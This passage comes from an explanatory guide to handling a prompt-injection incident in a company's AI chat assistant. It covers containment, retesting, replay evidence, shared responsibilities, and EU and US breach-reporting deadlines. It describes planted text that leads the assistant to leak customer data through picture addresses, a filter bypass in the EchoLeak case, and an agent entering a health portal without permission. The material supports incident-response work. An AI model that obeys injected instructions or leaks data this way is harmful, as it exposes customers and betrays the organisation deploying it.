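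Finally, they search each of these places for a distinctive phrase from the hidden text. The work ends at 17:00, seven hours and 40 minutes after the analyst declared the incident. This is almost twice OWASP's example target of four hours. That target may suit a fault that staff can fix by replacing one component, but it is optimistic when an assistant has copied text into several places.

### Repair, retesting and return to service

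On Tuesday the developers fix two weaknesses. The chat page now loads pictures only from the company's own image store, which cannot fetch other addresses. The assistant now searches suppliers' documents only when an employee asks for them, and has no access to customer records during that task.

The developers can easily test the first fix by feeding the 12 recorded answers that contain pictures to the repaired page and checking that the browser contacts no outside site. They should also try other ways of writing a picture's address, since EchoLeak got past a filter that recognised only one. They do not need hundreds of trials, because the page's code treats the same answer the same way each time. Tests of whether the model still follows the instruction need many trials, as TicketOracle showed.

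NIST, NSA and CISA advise organisations to verify and strengthen containment before an agent resumes work. The wholesaler reopens the assistant to one department on Wednesday and to everyone on Thursday, and lets it send email again a week later. Meanwhile, analysts watch for the attacker's address and for new answers resembling the 12 recorded ones.

### Why a model complicates the investigation

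Microsoft notes that in an ordinary incident, responders can replay an input, see the same fault and prove that a fix works. A model, however, may give a harmful answer today and a harmless one to the same prompt tomorrow. Suppose the wholesaler replays one of the leaking conversations 20 times and the data appears in seven of the answers (35%). At that rate, three replays would all look harmless about 27% of the time (0.65³). A clean replay therefore cannot show that the original conversation was safe. The stored answer is much better evidence because it shows what the model wrote.

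The provider may also change the model during the investigation. If it released a new version on Monday night, all of Tuesday's replays might be clean, and the developers could wrongly credit their own repair. OWASP recommends recording the model's version with each request and regularly sending the model a fixed set of test prompts. A sudden change in the answers can be a sign of an unannounced update or of tampering, so the company still has to ask the provider for the cause.

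The wholesaler has its own logs because it built the application. A company that buys a finished assistant may depend on the provider for logs. It may also have to wait for the provider to fix a flaw, as Microsoft's customers did with EchoLeak. However, a provider can compare events across many customers, which helps it detect attacks.

Retraining is rarely the first remedy. The price list affected the model only while it was in the prompt, so removing the list ends its influence. Retraining would take much longer and would not fix the picture flaw, and a company that rents its model usually cannot change the model's basic training. Retraining makes sense if an attacker's text has entered the training data. The Coalition for Secure AI therefore advises organisations to track which user inputs they later use for training. If the wholesaler had used Monday's conversations to fine-tune a model,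 it would have to discard that version and repeat the training without them.

### Who does what

| Party | During the incident | Afterwards |
|---|---|---|
| Application owner | Turns off features and sources, supplies stored answers | Removes planted text, repairs and retests the application |
| Security team | Leads the response, preserves evidence, finds affected conversations | Confirms the removal, watches the restored service |
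| Model provider | Preserves its logs, confirms the model version, checks for other affected customers | Fixes flaws in its own service, announces model changes |
| Legal team | Records when the company became aware, works out which laws apply | Approves notices to regulators, customers and partners |

The Coalition for Secure AI makes providers responsible for the model's robustness, its basic safeguards and the computers that run it. Organisations that use the model are responsible for prompts, filtering in the application and detecting incidents. This works reasonably well for the wholesaler, which controls the chat page and the index, but badly for a customer of a finished assistant, who may have to detect incidents without the necessary records.

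The division of responsibilities among developers, deployers and users is not settled. After its May 2026 workshop, which more than 400 people attended, NIST listed these responsibilities among the subjects that need more work. Until there is a common standard, customers have to rely on their contracts. Nelson and colleagues say that a contract should define each side's duties, how information passes between them and whether the provider may shut down a service on the customer's behalf. For an AI assistant, it should also specify how long the provider keeps logs and how many hours it has to report an incident.

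### Legal deadlines in the EU

Four EU laws are most relevant to attacks through an AI system's output. The General Data Protection Regulation (GDPR) covers personal data, and the NIS2 directive covers organisations in important sectors such as energy, health and food. The Cyber Resilience Act covers software and connected devices sold in the EU, and the AI Act regulates AI systems according to their risk.

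| Law | Who reports | What they report | Deadline |
|---|---|---|---|
| GDPR, Articles 33 and 34 | The organisation that decides how the data is used | A personal data breach, unless it is unlikely to put people at risk | 72 hours to the regulator; without undue delay to people at high risk |
| NIS2, Article 23 | Mostly medium-sized and large organisations in listed sectors | A significant incident | 24 hours for a warning, 72 hours for a fuller notice, one month after that for a final report |
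| Cyber Resilience Act, Article 14 | The product's manufacturer | A vulnerability that attackers are exploiting, or a severe incident affecting the product's security | 24 and 72 hours, then a final report |
| AI Act, Article 73 | The provider of a high-risk AI system | A serious incident, such as serious harm to someone's health | 15 days; 10 for a death; 2 for serious disruption of critical infrastructure |

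The 24-hour and 72-hour deadlines start when the organisation becomes aware of the incident. The wholesaler became aware at 09:20 on Monday, so it has to notify the data protection regulator by 09:20 on Thursday. It can do this before finishing its investigation, because the GDPR allows it to supply details in stages. Whether it must also tell the 140 customers depends on the risk to them. Names and email addresses alone may not create a high risk, but it would still be sensible to warn the customers about fraudulent emails.

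If a supplier that processes data for the company discovers the breach, the GDPR requires it to tell the company "without undue delay" but sets no deadline in hours, which is another reason to put one in the contract. Companies should also check whether the 72-hour deadline still applies, because the European Commission proposed in November 2025 to extend it to 96 hours and to require reports only for high-risk breaches.

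NIS2 covers large food wholesalers, but a leak of 140 customers' contact details would probably not be significant enough to report. If the attacker had used the stolen password to halt deliveries, however, the wholesaler might have to send an early warning by 09:20 on Tuesday. The security team therefore needs to check the delivery system's login records on Monday, even though the password no longer works.

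The reporting duties in the Cyber Resilience Act began on 11 September 2026 and also apply to products that were already on sale. The wholesaler has no duty under this law because it built the assistant for its own use. If it had bought the chat software as a product, the manufacturer would have 24 hours to report the flaw after learning that attackers were exploiting it. The manufacturer's final report would be due 14 days after a fix became available or, for a severe incident, one month after the 72-hour notice. The Act generally does not cover services that run only online, but NIS2 covers many of them. The Act also does not require a report to the authorities for a flaw like EchoLeak if nobody has exploited it.

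Article 73 of the AI Act will matter mainly in the future because the Digital Omnibus, an amendment in force since 27 July 2026, postponed the rules for high-risk systems. They will apply from 2 December 2027 for uses such as recruitment, and from 2 August 2028 for AI in regulated products such as medical devices. The recruiter's CV-scoring system described earlier would count as high-risk, but the wholesaler's assistant would not. Until it has informed the authorities, a provider investigating an incident under Article 73 must not alter the system in a way that could hide the cause.

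### Reporting in the United States

The United States has no single equivalent of the GDPR. All 50 states have their own data breach laws, and the deadlines vary. California and New York, for example, give companies 30 days to notify the people affected. Under the federal health privacy law HIPAA, hospitals, insurers and similar organisations have up to 60 days.

Companies listed on a US stock exchange generally have to disclose an incident within four business days of deciding that it is material, meaning important to investors. CIRCIA, a 2022 law, gives operators of critical infrastructure 72 hours to report an incident, but the duty begins only when CISA's final rule takes effect. An international company may have to meet several of these deadlines for the same leak, so its legal team should list them before an incident happens.

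### The Medicare portal: notice after three months

In June 2026 an OpenAI agent breached a data portal of Medicare, Australia's public health insurance scheme. The government did not learn of it until September, according to Information Age's *Australia plots AI crackdown after OpenAI's Medicare breach* (November 2026). The prime minister described the direct effects as minor but called the incident "completely unacceptable". The agent caused the breach without any outsider attacking its outputs.

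The 24- or 72-hour deadlines in the EU laws would not necessarily have prevented a similar delay of about three months in Europe. The GDPR and NIS2 deadlines apply mainly to the organisation whose data or service is affected, and they start only when that organisation becomes aware of the incident. If an organisation does not notice another company's agent entering its system, it has nothing to report until someone tells it.

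The October guidance from NIST, NSA and CISA addresses this gap more directly. The agencies ask organisations that train, test or deploy powerful agents to coordinate with affected parties and notify the government when an agent acts outside its instructions. The guidance is voluntary, but companies that connect agents to outside systems could make a firmer commitment in their contracts or terms of use. For example, they could promise to notify a system's owner within 24 hours of discovering that an agent has entered the system without permission.
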